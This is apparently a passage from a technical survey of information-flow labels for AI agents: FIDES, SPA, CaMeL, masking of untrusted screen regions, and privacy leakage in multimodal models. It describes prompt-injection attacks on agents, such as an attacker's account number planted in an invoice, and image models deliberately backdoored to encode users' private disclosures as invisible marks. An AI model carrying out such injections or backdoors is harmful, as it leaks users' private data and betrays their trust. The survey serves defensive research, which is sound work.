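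Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes experimental versions of these ideas in software that developers already use. Its main example of an accidental leak involves an employee, Alex, who asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales figures. Marco, who is not authorised to see them yet, has written to ask about sales. Once the agent has read both emails, anything it writes has the label

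{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex},

so it may not send a reply to Marco on its own. If Priya had copied Marco in, the label would have been {Alex, Marco} and the reply could have gone out.

The same rule blocks a harmless reply. The agent cannot answer Priya about her own figures, because Priya is not on the reader list of Marco's email. If the agent handled each email in a separate context, its reply to Priya would have the label {Alex, Priya}, and the rule would allow it.

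The prototypes pass labels between programs using the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way for AI applications to connect to tools and data. Microsoft uses the protocol's general-purpose metadata fields to carry labels for a whole tool call or for a single argument. Applications that do not recognise the labels can ignore them. A server can also use metadata fields to publish a policy for each tool. GitHub's MCP server now offers labels as an optional feature. It marks files and issues from public repositories as public and untrusted, and those from private repositories as private and trusted. For servers that do not support labels, Microsoft has released a gateway that adds them, although someone must write or choose the labelling rules for each tool.

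GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding assistant, has an experimental setting that maintains a context label and updates it after every tool result. The setting enforces policies only for selected tools on GitHub's own MCP server and does not yet support other servers.

The version in Agent Framework, Microsoft's toolkit for building agents, is closer to the full FIDES design. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced it in May as an experimental feature. By default, the feature hides untrusted tool results in variables and sends them to a quarantined model when the agent needs to process them. The announcement lists several limitations. Once untrusted content enters the main model's context, the rest of the run is untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes that content. The quarantined model can answer only one query at a time, with no follow-up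 conversation. Approval requests show users which tool and label caused them, but not the label's full history. The feature is available only in Python so far.

Developers also have to label their own data sources. According to the May announcement, the software would treat unlabelled tool results as trusted and public. In Microsoft's current documentation, the default is untrusted and public, which is safer against injected instructions but does nothing to protect secrets. If a tool returned patient photos without a label, the software would treat them as public.

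Agent Framework automatically hides only untrusted data, so a private but trusted file goes straight into the main model's context and restricts everything after it. Microsoft's sample policy for posting to a Teams channel allows any message written in a trusted context, whoever is in the channel. This prevents an attacker from triggering a leak, but the model can still leak confidential content by mistake. The published examples all use text, such as emails, source files and bug reports, although the same metadata could label an image or a recording.

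### Labels that survive storage

Agents increasingly keep results from one request for use in another. Girrens and Wang (2026) designed *SPA*, a text-based agent system, to preserve labels when this happens. In their example, a user asks an agent on Monday to retrieve an invoice and remember its details, which include an attacker's account number. The number becomes dangerous only on Tuesday, when the user tells the agent to pay the invoice they discussed the day before.

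SPA stores each result as a value with its label and a description. The description gives the format of the result, the query that produced it and a note on what it represents. On Tuesday, the planner receives only the descriptions. The notes cannot contain hidden instructions from the invoice, because Monday's planner wrote them before any tool had run.

If Tuesday's plan needs the invoice, it must include an explicit retrieval step, which restores the value with its original label. Before anything runs, a checker works out the label of every step in the plan and rejects the plan if any step would break a policy. A payment tool that requires trusted arguments would therefore reject the account number on Tuesday just as it would have on Monday. The planner writes one plan per request and cannot try again if the checker rejects it.

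In tests on AgentDojo with the small model gpt-5.4-nano, turning on these strict flow checks reduced the share of tasks SPA completed from 53.0% to 29.0%. About half of the runs with checks ended because the checker rejected the plan, typically for passing untrusted tool output to an action that required trusted data. The checks improved measured security only slightly, because writing the plan in advance had already defeated nearly all the attacks. Four of 949 attacks succeeded without the checks and none with them.

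Girrens and Wang also split the AgentDojo tasks into sequences of two to five requests. On these sequences, the checks reduced completion from 62.5% to 35.3%. When a later request needed a result that an earlier one had stored, the later plan retrieved it 89.9% of the time with checks on, so hiding the stored values did not usually prevent the planner from finding them. The attacks were not designed to stay inactive until a later request, so the test provides little evidence of how well SPA would resist attacks that were.

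### The case against conservative merge

Some systems researchers doubt that labels can remain useful once they pass through a language model. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), a group from Google, Meta and several universities, put the case in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*. They argue that software currently has no safe alternative to conservative merge, and that the rule defeats the purpose of tracking labels. Their argument can be set out in three premises:

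1. Any input to a model may influence any part of its output.
2. A sound label must cover every possible influence.
3. Contexts mix data with many different labels.

It follows that every output carries every label in its context, and label explosion sets in as agents feed those outputs into new contexts.

The first premise describes what software can rule out, not how models behave. Xu and colleagues found that some inputs have no visible effect on the output, but a system that cannot identify those inputs in advance must label the output as if every input affected it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, a later paper by members of the same group, suggests narrowing the labels by measuring influence, for example by removing an input and observing how the model's actions change. The second premise is close to a definition of soundness, and without it the labels provide an estimate rather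 than a guarantee.

The third premise depends on how developers build the system, and FIDES, CaMeL and LLMbda all work by making it false. Suppose a system makes several model calls, and call i receives only the set of inputs Sᵢ. The label of its output yᵢ is then

ℓ(yᵢ) = ⨆ ℓ(x) over all x in Sᵢ.

This label is never more restrictive than the join over everything the system has read, and it is often much less restrictive. Sᵢ must include everything that influenced the prompt or the decision to make the call, so the planner's own context must stay free of restricted data.

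Conservative merge can be usable even without isolation, since the o3-mini agent that used it with no hiding finished more tasks unaided than the agent without labels. But the basic agent's results on the Slack tasks show how quickly the merged labels can become restrictive when an agent reads messages from many people.

### What isolation costs

Isolation works best on tasks that Costa and colleagues call data-independent, where one sequence of tool calls and one final response would succeed whatever the data contained. Sending a summary of three emails is data-independent because the agent takes the same steps regardless of their content. Checking the emails for a meeting request, and creating a calendar event only if there is one, is data-dependent because the planner needs information from the emails to choose the next step.

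Data-dependent tasks make up 5% of AgentDojo's workspace tasks and 10% of its travel tasks, but 43.8% of its banking tasks and 42.9% of its Slack tasks. Many of the banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it. Under FIDES, reading the file makes the context untrusted, so the software blocks the payment. Costa and colleagues regard most of these failures as intended, since the agent cannot tell a genuine bill from an attacker's.

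CaMeL can handle some of these tasks by including a conditional in its program, such as "if there is a meeting request, create the event", but it cannot include one for an instruction that nobody anticipated.

A user can sometimes resolve the problem by vouching for the data. In Prudentia, the planner can ask the user to endorse an untrusted item before revealing it, so if an email contains a to-do list of ten actions, one endorsement replaces ten separate approvals. With o4-mini, Prudentia needed 19.2 human interventions across the tasks it completed and FIDES needed 36.8, though FIDES completed slightly more tasks (75.7% against 73.2%). Prudentia's agent still asks the user about each call that would release private information, because its designers thought that decision depended too much on the situation for blanket permission.

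### The hospital assistant with separate contexts

The hospital's modular pipeline could follow FIDES's rules, although the published results for FIDES, CaMeL and SPA cover only text and tool calls. The planner starts with Ada's request and the style guide, which are both trusted and public. The software hides the whiteboard photo and the voice memo in variables, so the context label does not change.

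To make the poster, the planner writes a prompt from the style guide and sends it to the image generator. The generator must start with an empty conversation so it cannot edit the photo. The poster is then trusted and open to everyone, so it can go on the corridor wall.

For the announcement, a speech recogniser transcribes the memo, and the software gives the transcript the memo's label. A quarantined model turns the transcript into an announcement, and a speech synthesiser reads it out. Each result keeps the reader list {Ada, Ben, Cam}, so Cam may hear the recording. Cam was not allowed to hear it when all three outputs shared a context.

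The script needs both the memo and the photo. A quarantined model that accepts images can read them together, but the script it writes is untrusted, and only Ada and Ben may read it. Isolating the model does not improve this label, because the script depends on both items. The policy check stops the script from running automatically, so Ada must either approve the script or endorse the photo.

Now suppose a unified model receives the photo, the memo and the style guide together and generates all three outputs. The software can label the inputs, but once the model is running, it can't hide the photo from the part of the computation that draws the poster. So it labels every output as untrusted and restricted to Ada and Ben.

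The hospital could run the unified model three times, giving it only the relevant items each time. The labels would then match those of the modular pipeline, because they depend on which items share a context, not on how many models are used. But the model could no longer use all the items at once, for example to match the wording of the announcement to the poster, and that ability is a main reason to choose a unified model.

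The software would also have to separate the items before the first call. If Ada attached the photo to her message, FIDES's default for user messages would label the photo trusted and public, so the hospital would need a separate rule for attachments.

Isolation fails for some requests in either design. Ada might ask for a poster appealing for volunteers only if the memo reports a staff shortage. The planner would then need a yes-or-no answer from the memo. Reading that answer would restrict the planner's context to Ada, Ben and Cam, and the poster would inherit the restriction even if its design came entirely from the style guide. The restriction is justified here because anyone who saw the poster in the corridor would learn that the ward was short of staff.

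## Labelling images, audio, screenshots and generated code

FIDES would hide the hospital's whiteboard photo behind one variable with one label. But the board might show patients' initials in one column and visiting hours in the next, and only the initials need protection. Separate labels would let the assistant put the visiting hours on a poster. Someone would first have to mark the boundary between the columns, and software would have to keep that boundary accurate as other programs crop, compress or describe the photo.

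### What a label can cover

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists trackers that work at scales from single processor instructions to whole computers. In a multimodal pipeline, a tracker could label anything from a whole file to a few pixels, seconds of audio or lines of code.

| Unit | Who can assign the label | What can strip or blur it |
|---|---|---|
| Whole file | Its owner, or the software that saves it | Uploading it or copying it to a system that ignores labels |
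| Region of a picture or screen | A website's owner, a person who draws a box, or a model that finds sensitive areas | Taking a screenshot, or editing the picture with a generative model |
| Span of a recording | A person or program that marks start and end times | Re-recording it, or cutting it so that the times shift |
| Transcript | The speech-recognition software, from the recording's label | Pasting the words into a message |
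| Embedding | The software that runs the encoder, from the input's label | Saving the vector in a database with no field for labels |
| Line of code | The software that calls the model | Moving or rewriting the line |

A whole file is the easiest unit to track. *Flowsh* records which files a command opens and which servers send it data, then passes the labels of those inputs to the command's outputs. If a command converts a PDF to text, the text file inherits the PDF's label, even though the tracker does not parse either format. The same rule would cover a command that crops a photo or compresses a recording.

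*Flowsh* stores the label in the file's extended attributes, which are part of the filesystem, not the file's contents. The label therefore survives renaming, but sending the file as an email attachment would normally remove it. The label also applies to the whole file, so a crop showing only the visiting hours would still be restricted to Ada and Ben.

Even so, file labels can spare users many approval requests. On office-style knowledge work, a permissive sandbox that asked for approval whenever it could not guarantee that an action was safe needed 5.8 times as many approvals per completed task as *Flowsh*. On Terminal-Bench, a set of command-line tasks, it needed 22.5 times as many. However, *Flowsh* completed 7.9 percentage points fewer tasks on the office-style work and 9.7 points fewer on Terminal-Bench.

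Finer labels for sound would apply to stretches of time. Suppose the first minute of the voice memo covers the rota and the second names a nurse on sick leave. If the transcriber records the time of each word, software could carry the second minute's label to the matching words. But speech recognisers use surrounding speech to resolve unclear words, so a word from the first minute could depend on the second. Cutting the recording at the boundary and transcribing each part separately would avoid this dependence, as separate contexts do for a language model.

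An embedding, a vector that represents an item for a model, is harder to divide. A single vector for the whiteboard photo mixes information from both columns, so the only safe label for it is the label of the whole photo. Splitting the photo into patches does not solve the problem if the encoder passes information between patches before it produces their vectors.

### Conversions that lose labels

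A label survives a conversion that the tracking software performs or monitors, but is lost when the conversion happens elsewhere. If Ben photographs his screen with his phone, the photo shows the same patients' initials but has no label. The label is also lost if another device records the memo as it plays over a speaker, or if Ada copies two lines of the transcript into a chat.

Re-encoding can also separate a label from its content. A messaging service that shrinks the whiteboard photo may discard the metadata that holds the label but leave the initials readable. The hospital could treat every unlabelled file as restricted, which would protect the shrunken photo but also block every ordinary picture from outside.

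Long-running agents also convert their own history when they summarise it or drop old images to save space. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) points out that an agent cannot retake an old screenshot once the interface has changed, and that nobody has measured whether constraints survive when an agent compacts its visual history. Keeping every full screenshot across a thousand state transfers would take hundreds of megabytes to gigabytes, compared with about half a megabyte for pointers to text. It would also create an archive of any private data that appeared on screen.

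### Signed provenance metadata

One way to keep a label with a file is to sign the label and embed it in the file. The Coalition for Content Provenance and Authenticity (C2PA) publishes a standard for doing this with information about a file's origin. In C2PA's *Content Credentials*, a camera or editing program writes statements called assertions, lists them in a digitally signed claim, and embeds the whole package, called a manifest, in a file such as a JPEG. A viewer's software checks the signature and shows the assertions so that the viewer can judge how far to trust the picture.

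The C2PA format could hold a reader list. Its standard assertions include regions of interest, which could mark one column of a whiteboard. Another assertion lists ingredients, the earlier files that went into a new one, and software could join their labels. *Metadata Assertion*, a specification from outside C2PA, provides a way to include metadata that C2PA's built-in assertion no longer accepts.

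However, confidentiality also requires programs to enforce the label. A valid signature shows who attached the reader list and that nobody has altered it since, but a program that doesn't check the list can still display the photo to anyone. The hospital would need a check at every sink, as it would with any other label format.

Removing the manifest from a news photo gives viewers less reason to trust it, while removing it from a patient photo may make the file look public. C2PA's implementation guidance allows a program to redact assertions if the new manifest records the redaction. That is sensible for hiding a photographer's location, but a confidentiality system would have to treat removing a reader list as a release that needs authority.

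The guidance recommends creating manifests only at significant events, such as when a file is created or exported, because signing takes effort. A label tracker, however, has to update its labels at every step in between. Signed metadata therefore suits transfers between organisations that both enforce labels, with each organisation running its own tracker internally.

The manifest must also stay attached to the right picture. An online explainer, *hard bindings vs soft bindings*, describes C2PA's two methods for this. A cryptographic hash identifies the exact bytes, so any re-encoding breaks the match, while a watermark or perceptual fingerprint survives moderate changes. With a fingerprint, the hospital could recognise the shrunken whiteboard photo and look up its label, but a new poster that mentioned one of the patients would not match.

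### Masking parts of a screen

The existing systems closest to region labelling are computer-use agents, which operate programs by looking at the screen, clicking and typing. The screen can mix trusted and untrusted content. A shopping page, for example, shows the shop's own buttons alongside reviews and advertisements that an attacker could have written. Integrity is the label that matters here, and several groups have built agents that keep untrusted regions away from the model that chooses the actions.

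*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) avoids labelling regions of the screen by hiding every screenshot from the planner. As in the original CaMeL, the planner writes its whole program in advance. A quarantined vision model supplies descriptions and coordinates, and another quarantined model chooses between the program's branches by answering yes-or-no questions, such as whether a cookie banner is visible.

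Planning without seeing the screen makes the programs long. They averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 tool calls and 4 branches on AgentDojo's text tasks. Foerster and colleagues tested the design on OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop tasks. Of the 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed without protection, the protected version completed 28.4% on the first attempt and 56.9% within five attempts.

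A planner can do better if it sees the trusted part of the screen. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) uses a web page's underlying structure to replace untrusted regions with placeholders such as "user comment". On a shopping site, the planner still sees the layout, the buttons and the shop's own text. To learn about a hidden review, it names the placeholder, asks a question and specifies the type of answer (yes or no, a number, a date or a choice from a list). A quarantined model reads the review and answers, and software rejects any answer of the wrong type. One version also allows free-text answers if the user approves them.

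On ten purpose-built websites, masking preserved the agents' success rates and multiplied the typical cost of a task by 1.05 to 1.84. About 15% of tasks became cheaper, which Nikolić and colleagues attribute to less clutter on the page. They also planted strengthened versions of known injections, and none succeeded.

### Who marks the regions

These results assume that the website's owner labels the untrusted regions. For GitLab, Booking.com and Reddit, 15 to 30 handwritten rules per site were enough. Nikolić and colleagues also had a language model propose the rules from the page's structure, with all text removed so that hidden instructions could not influence the model. By their counts, it missed about 7% of the types of untrusted element on Booking.com, 10% on GitLab and none on Reddit.

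*Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (Seip, Markovinović and Hein, 2026) repeated the automatic labelling on 115 captured web pages and got much worse results. With two other models proposing the rules, 44.1% and 36.7% of the untrusted free-text items stayed visible. The paper counted individual items instead of types and used a broader definition of untrusted content, which may explain part of the difference. Either set of error rates would break a strict guarantee, because one visible instruction can redirect an agent.

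The SA-CUA system starts with the page or document content masked and unmasks only the regions that its rules identify as trusted. It finds these regions in the accessibility tree, the description of on-screen elements that software provides for screen readers, so it also works in desktop programs. If the tree omits a region, that region stays hidden. In 160 captures, no untrusted free text remained visible. However, the system also hid 56.3% or 76.9% of the trusted items on web pages, depending on which model wrote its rules.

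SA-CUA gives each click the label of the region under the cursor and blocks clicks on buttons in untrusted regions. Values from hidden regions stay hidden from the planner until a check endorses them. For example, a user might ask for a Python package that prints coloured text, and a forum post might name one. Before the planner sees that name, the system forms an expectation from trusted information and compares the name with it. An attacker can make the comparison fail but cannot argue for a different package.

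*Secure-CUA* (Choudhary, Christodorescu and colleagues, 2026) lets the agent see a new masked screenshot before every action. One model uses the screenshot to write a short program that specifies which questions to ask about hidden regions and how to use the answers. If the task is to copy a customer review into a description field, a symbolic reference stands in for the review. Another model locates the field on the masked screenshot, and ordinary software then inserts the text. The software also masks that text in later screenshots, so the review keeps its label in its new position on the screen.

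The systems differ in what the planner sees and what it can get back from hidden content:

| System | What the planner sees | What hidden content can return |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL for computer use | No screen | Descriptions, coordinates and verdicts, used only by the finished program |
| Untrusted Content Masking | The page, with untrusted regions masked | Yes or no, numbers, dates or a listed choice, with free text if the user approves |
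| Secure-CUA | A new masked screen before each action | Limited values used by the program, and free text as a symbolic reference |
| SA-CUA | The screen, with only trusted regions unmasked | A value of a set type, hidden until a check endorses it |

### Security and lost tasks

Seip and colleagues compared SA-CUA with an unprotected agent and with CaMeL for computer use. The table gives the results as percentages, with Qwen3.8-27B as the planner. In the attack tests, harmful instructions were planted among information the agent needed for its task.

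| Measure | Unprotected | CaMeL for computer use | SA-CUA |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attacks that succeeded at least once in three runs | 46.2 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Tasks completed under attack | 95.4 | 18.5 | 86.2 |
| Ordinary OSWorld tasks completed | 58.3 | 8.3 | 30.6 |
| Ordinary web tasks from Nikolić and colleagues completed | 90.9 | 9.1 | 50.5 |

SA-CUA completed most of the attacked tasks but only about half as many ordinary tasks as the unprotected agent. Several ordinary tasks require acting on untrusted information that no other source can confirm, such as a seller's description of a laptop's condition.

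Choudhary and colleagues report a much smaller drop in task completion on 400 web tasks without attacks. Averaged over three models and five runs, Secure-CUA completed 53.55% of the tasks, an unprotected agent 55.12% and CaMeL for computer use 13.17%. Secure-CUA took about three times as long as the unprotected agent. Its security rests on a proof that assumes handwritten rules have labelled every untrusted element correctly. In both comparisons, CaMeL's low scores were obtained in a rival group's set-up.

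These agents process screenshots, so their results apply to images as inputs, not to labels on generated pictures. Even with masking, misleading content may lead a quarantined model to give a false answer of the permitted kind, a problem SA-CUA's endorsement check addresses. If an agent locates buttons on an unmasked screen, misleading content may also make it click the wrong one. Secure-CUA addresses this with a masked search for buttons.

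### Reader lists for screen regions

All four systems protect integrity. Seip and colleagues state that SA-CUA does not protect confidentiality, so the agent could still post private information on a public forum. Masks could hide secrets as well as untrusted text, but several design choices would have to change.

A date is a safe answer to accept from an untrusted web page because it is too short to contain an instruction, but a hospital may have to hide a patient's date of birth. SA-CUA can unmask untrusted items that match patterns for prices, dates and reference numbers. If the same rule were applied to confidential data, it could expose an appointment or a patient number. A system that protects secrets has to label any answer drawn from a hidden region with that region's reader list, however short the answer is.

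Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *SPIDES*, built such a system for web browsing. Website owners attach an integrity label and a reader list to parts of a page, where the readers are the user and named websites. The software then hides elements by the same rule as FIDES. For a context open to readers R_ctx and an element open to readers R, it hides the element whenever

R_ctx ⊈ R,

which means that someone who may receive the context is not allowed to see the element. A saved card number might be open only to the user and shop.com. If the agent chooses to look at it, its context narrows to those two readers, and sending anything to another site then needs the user's approval.

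The researchers tested this on 28 linked websites with 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks, including attempts to steal data. They let the attacker choose the model's output whenever untrusted content entered its context, and no attack succeeded. With five models, the agent completed 67.1% to 86.1% of the ordinary tasks.

The agent reads a text description of each page, not a screenshot, so the experiment shows that reader lists work on parts of a page but doesn't test them on pixels. Zverev and colleagues treat unlabelled elements on a trusted site as public. If the hospital's patient portal used this default and its owner forgot to label a new field, the agent could send the field's contents anywhere.

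When an agent's model runs on a company's servers, the company becomes another recipient of everything in the screenshots. *CAPED* (2026) masks private elements on the phone before uploading the image. It aims to hide details the task does not need while leaving enough visible for the agent to act. It does not ask the remote model what to hide, because that would disclose the screen. Foerster and colleagues suggest having a local model read the screen instead, so that the remote planner never receives it.

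Phone-based masking usually depends on detecting sensitive content, so it shares the weaknesses of a content filter. *GUIGuard-Bench* (2026) attributes undermasking and overmasking to detector errors. The paper also describes replacing private values that a task needs with plausible fakes, so the agent can still see what kind of information belongs there.

### Images with no single correct label

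A label can be wrong when it is first assigned, even if every later conversion preserves it, because whether someone may share a picture depends on the situation. The theory of contextual integrity defines privacy as a flow of information that fits the norms of its setting. *MPCI-Bench* (Wang and Zhang, 2026) describes each flow by the person the data concerns, the sender, the recipient, the type of data and the condition for sharing it. In one example, an event photographer may send a picture of a festival participant in traditional dress to a cultural archivist, but not to an employer screening the participant for a job.

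The benchmark contains 1,026 such pairs, each built from one image. A language model wrote an appropriate and an inappropriate situation for every image and expanded both into short stories. The researchers then turned the stories into simulated office tasks, in which an agent can read messages and files and send an email or chat message. The table gives the percentage of cases in which selected models shared data:

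| Model | Private text, inappropriate case | Image, inappropriate case | Image, appropriate case |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 20.2 | 56.9 | 92.0 |
| Mistral Large 3 | 38.7 | 82.1 | 97.3 |
| GPT-4o | 40.9 | 90.4 | 98.3 |
| Qwen3-VL-30B | 45.2 | 91.6 | 97.4 |

Some of the gap between text and images may come from the design. In the stories, the image is useful for the task, while the private text is a separate detail that appears with harmless text. An agent can therefore omit the private text and still send a helpful message, but omitting the image means doing less of what the user asked. GPT-4o also both wrote the cases and judged the results. Leakage is still high in absolute terms, although newer models may be more careful.

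The models could often identify whether sharing was appropriate in these office tasks, even when they leaked content. Qwen3-VL-30B was right 90.4% of the time when asked directly. Adding a prompt that made the agent check privacy norms before acting reduced Mistral Large 3's image leaks from 82.1% to 29.6%, while its appropriate sharing fell only from 97.3% to 92.0%. A general instruction to reason first cut leaks further, to 8.6%, but also reduced appropriate sharing to 13.4%.

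A deterministic label check could stop many of these leaks if the reader list were right, since on average 59% of them consisted only of attaching the image file. But a reader list can only distinguish between readers, such as the archivist and the employer, and not between two purposes for the same reader. Ben may need the whiteboard photo to plan shifts but have no right to use it to find out whether his neighbour is in hospital. To enforce that, the label would also have to record the permitted purpose, and the check at the sink would need reliable evidence of what Ben was doing.

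*MaskClaw* (2026) uses context to decide what to mask before a screenshot leaves the device. This makes the policy more flexible than a fixed reader list, which only requires the software to compare names, but the policy's correctness then depends on how well the software interprets the context.

### Generated code

Generated code also needs a label when the model writes it, because the code may contain a secret or reflect one. Unlike a picture, a program has defined operations that other software can check and track when the program runs.

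*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) uses this property in Elba, an agent system for the programming language Haskell. The developer specifies the type that the model's program must have. Haskell types describe both the kind of result and the effects a program may have, such as writing files or using the network. The typechecker rejects the program before it runs if it does anything the type doesn't allow. The model can then correct the error and try again.

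Elba controls information flow with LIO, an existing Haskell library. The type check ensures that the generated program can act only through LIO's operations, which check labels as the program runs. It does not prove that the program respects every label. LIO's current label works like the context label in FIDES, but it covers a running program instead of a conversation. A program can keep its current label unchanged by running one part separately and receiving a sealed result.

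Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the language guarantees for all well-typed programs also holds for programs that call a model, provided the typechecker accepts the model's code before it runs. The proof replaces each model call with an ordinary function that obtains the code, checks it and runs it. The two programs behave identically, so the guarantee carries over. Unlike LLMbda's theorem, the proof does not cover leaks through sampling probabilities, because it treats the model as a fixed function from prompts to programs.

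The researchers tested Elba on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks, which involve text and tool calls. With policies on, it completed 8 to 10 tasks, depending on the model, and CaMeL completed 4 to 6. In a harsher test, they made the models follow any planted instruction directly. Between 15.5% and 42.2% of attacks succeeded without the policies, and none succeeded with them. The policies also reduced the share of tasks completed under attack from 67–76% to 40–48%.

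The benefit of this second stage depends on what the model read before writing the code. Suppose it writes the hospital's scheduling script from Ada's request alone. The script starts with a public label, and when it runs, LIO can assign the reader list {Ada, Ben, Cam} to a value calculated from the memo. Only values that depend on the photo need the shorter list {Ada, Ben}. If the model had read the photo first, the whole script would start with the shorter list, and running it could not safely remove that restriction.

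*Flowsh* can track programs in any language, but it gives everything a command produces the same label. Elba, which requires Haskell and a library of approved operations, can label values separately within one program.

A finished image or recording has no equivalent second stage. Opening the poster or playing the announcement runs the same decoding steps whatever inputs influenced the content, so monitoring those steps can't show which inputs did. The software therefore has to assign the label when the model generates the file. It may be able to label regions separately, depending on how much they affect each other.

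Pictures that a program draws are an exception. If the model writes code for a staffing chart and the code reads the rota only when it runs, a system like Elba could track the rota into the chart. The hospital could then get a more precise label by asking the model for drawing code instead of a finished picture.

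## How much context reaches outputs in another modality

Conservative merge labels a generated picture as if everything in the context had influenced it. The less often a disclosure in a chat shows up in a later picture, the more that label overstates the risk.

In October 2026, Braun and colleagues measured how much of a chat's context reaches the images generated from it. They built pairs of chats that ended with the same image request, taken from the captions of a standard photo collection. Only one chat in each pair contained a sensitive statement, such as "I am pregnant", which was unrelated to the request. For each of five topics, they generated 500 images from chats with the statement and 500 from chats without it.

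They then converted every image into an embedding using CLIP, a model that represents pictures and captions in one vector space. They trained a probe, a simple linear classifier, on 90% of the embeddings to tell which kind of chat had produced an image, and tested it on the other 10%. This test is a statistical version of generating the hospital's poster once for each diagnosis and comparing the results.

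On BAGEL, an open unified model, the probe did little better than guessing. On OmniGen2, another open model, it could often tell the images apart, especially for pregnancy, where the pictures showed visible traces of the earlier statement. Two other open models, Show-o2 and Emu3.5, often drew things from earlier turns that the final request had not mentioned. Braun and colleagues give example images for these two but no rates, and they left both out of their later experiments, which were about leaks users would not notice.

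The BAGEL result does not establish noninterference. Each test set would have held about 100 images, so chance alone would typically move a useless probe's accuracy by about 5 percentage points, enough to hide a small leak. CLIP embeddings mainly capture what a picture shows, so the probe could also have missed faint patterns in the pixels. The disclosures were typed, so the experiment provides little evidence about a photo or recording in the context.

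### Invisible marks from altered models

Braun and colleagues also deliberately altered BAGEL and OmniGen2 so that a particular disclosure would make the model put an invisible mark on later, unrelated pictures. Anyone who knew what to look for could then test a picture the user had posted online, without seeing the chat. Running the model on the user's own computer would not prevent this, because the information leaves with the picture.

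The researchers tested 13 disclosures in wordings they had not used when altering the models. Some were indirect, such as "My due date is coming up next month" for pregnancy. The table shows the percentage of marked pictures they detected at a threshold that wrongly flagged 1% of pictures from chats without the disclosure. Each range covers chats with zero to three unrelated exchanges between the disclosure and the image request.

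| Disclosure | OmniGen2 | BAGEL |
|---|---|---|
| Depression | 100.0 | 94.2–99.8 |
| Being Hindu | 98.6–99.6 | 91.4–98.2 |
| Pregnancy | 58.6–80.4 | 95.8–98.0 |
| Average of ten others | 41.7–60.0 | 72.9–92.4 |

Detection was less reliable for some disclosures when the image requests came from a different collection. On BAGEL, the average for the ten other disclosures fell to between 36.7% and 65.8%. Even if detection caught every true case, a single flagged picture would leave some doubt. If 1 user in 100 had mentioned depression, a threshold with 1% false alarms would flag about as many pictures from other users as from those who had mentioned it. Several flagged pictures from the same chat would give stronger evidence.

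A single altered model could also reveal which of several things a user had said. Braun and colleagues altered one version of OmniGen2 to put a different mark in its images for each of three disclosures, and the correct mark was the most readable of the three in all 1,500 test images.

The marks usually survived when the researchers shrank, blurred, sharpened or compressed the pictures, or changed their brightness, contrast or saturation. With a threshold that allowed 5% false alarms, average detection fell only from 95.6% to 95.3% on OmniGen2 and from 97.5% to 96.7% on BAGEL. Heavy JPEG compression reduced detection the most. At the stricter threshold, it lowered detection of one political disclosure on OmniGen2 from 100% to 67%. Because the marks usually survive, a messaging service that re-encodes a picture could remove its label but leave the hidden mark.

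Inspecting the pictures was a weak defence. Braun and colleagues trained two classifiers to separate marked pictures from clean ones using general image statistics, such as noise and frequency patterns. They measured performance by AUC, the probability that a classifier ranks a random marked picture above a random clean one, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. Most scores were between 0.63 and 0.79, and for one disclosure on OmniGen2 both classifiers were close to guessing. The classifiers were also trained on examples of marked and clean pictures, which a hospital checking a suspicious model would not normally have.

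Other checks did no better. Two prompt-injection scanners flagged none of the chats, because the disclosures were ordinary sentences. The altered models scored exactly the same as the originals on a test of image understanding, and their picture quality was mostly unchanged.

### Written text that changes the rest of a picture

When a prompt asks an image model to include specific words, as on a poster, those words can also affect the rest of the image. *When Scene Text Hijacks the Scene* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tests this with four open image models and two commercial ones, GPT-Image-2 and Nano-Banana-2. In one example, the prompt describes a bus station with a large sign that says "A brown leather suitcase by the door." A suitcase in the resulting image would suggest that the model had used the words as more than lettering.

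The researchers chose 60 visual changes, such as adding a dog or making the scene foggy. They tried six requests for each change, varying the wording and the surrounding scene, and mentioned the change only in the text to be written in the picture. Before scoring an image, they used text-recognition software to find the writing and blurred it, or painted over it if it was still readable. A vision-language model then judged whether the change appeared in the rest of the picture.

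On LongCat, the least affected model, at least one of the six requests produced 71.7% of the 60 changes, compared with 98.3% on each commercial model. Images made from the same scene descriptions with different written text did not pass the threshold, so the scene descriptions alone do not explain the result. The judge tended to undercount changes. It missed about 18% of the changes human reviewers saw, and the reviewers agreed with about 97% of the changes it reported.

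These rates reflect what a determined user could achieve more than how often content leaks by accident, because one success in six was enough and the text always described something easy to draw. A patient's initials would probably affect the scene less. Better lettering does not solve the problem, since the commercial models usually wrote the relevant words correctly in the images where the leak was strong.

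This undermines the idea of labelling regions of a generated picture separately. Suppose Ada asks for a staff notice that includes the restricted line "Measles on Ward 3". Software might label the rectangle around that line {Ada, Ben} and the rest of the notice public, then cover the rectangle to make a version for the corridor. But the model could have drawn a child with a rash beside the text, and that drawing would still be visible. Li and colleagues' masking step is almost the same as this redaction, so their scores measure what would remain after it.

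Region labels on inputs do not have this weakness, because software can hide a region before the model receives the input. The hospital could make region labels reliable on an output by generating the background in a model call that excludes the restricted line, then adding the lettering with ordinary software. The line's label would then need to cover only the pixels the software drew, provided nothing else about the layout depended on the line.

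Changing the model itself has helped only partly. The open model FLUX-2-dev generates an image by starting from noise and refining it in steps. Li and colleagues saw the scene take shape before the letters became legible, which suggests that the meaning of the text influences the scene early. They suppressed part of the text's representation during the first 20 steps and restored it later so that the model could still draw the letters. On 120 requests that hid harmful content in the written text, the leakage rate fell from 97.5% to 65.0%. In pictures with several pieces of text, the share of words rendered correctly also fell, from 93.7% to 86.7%.

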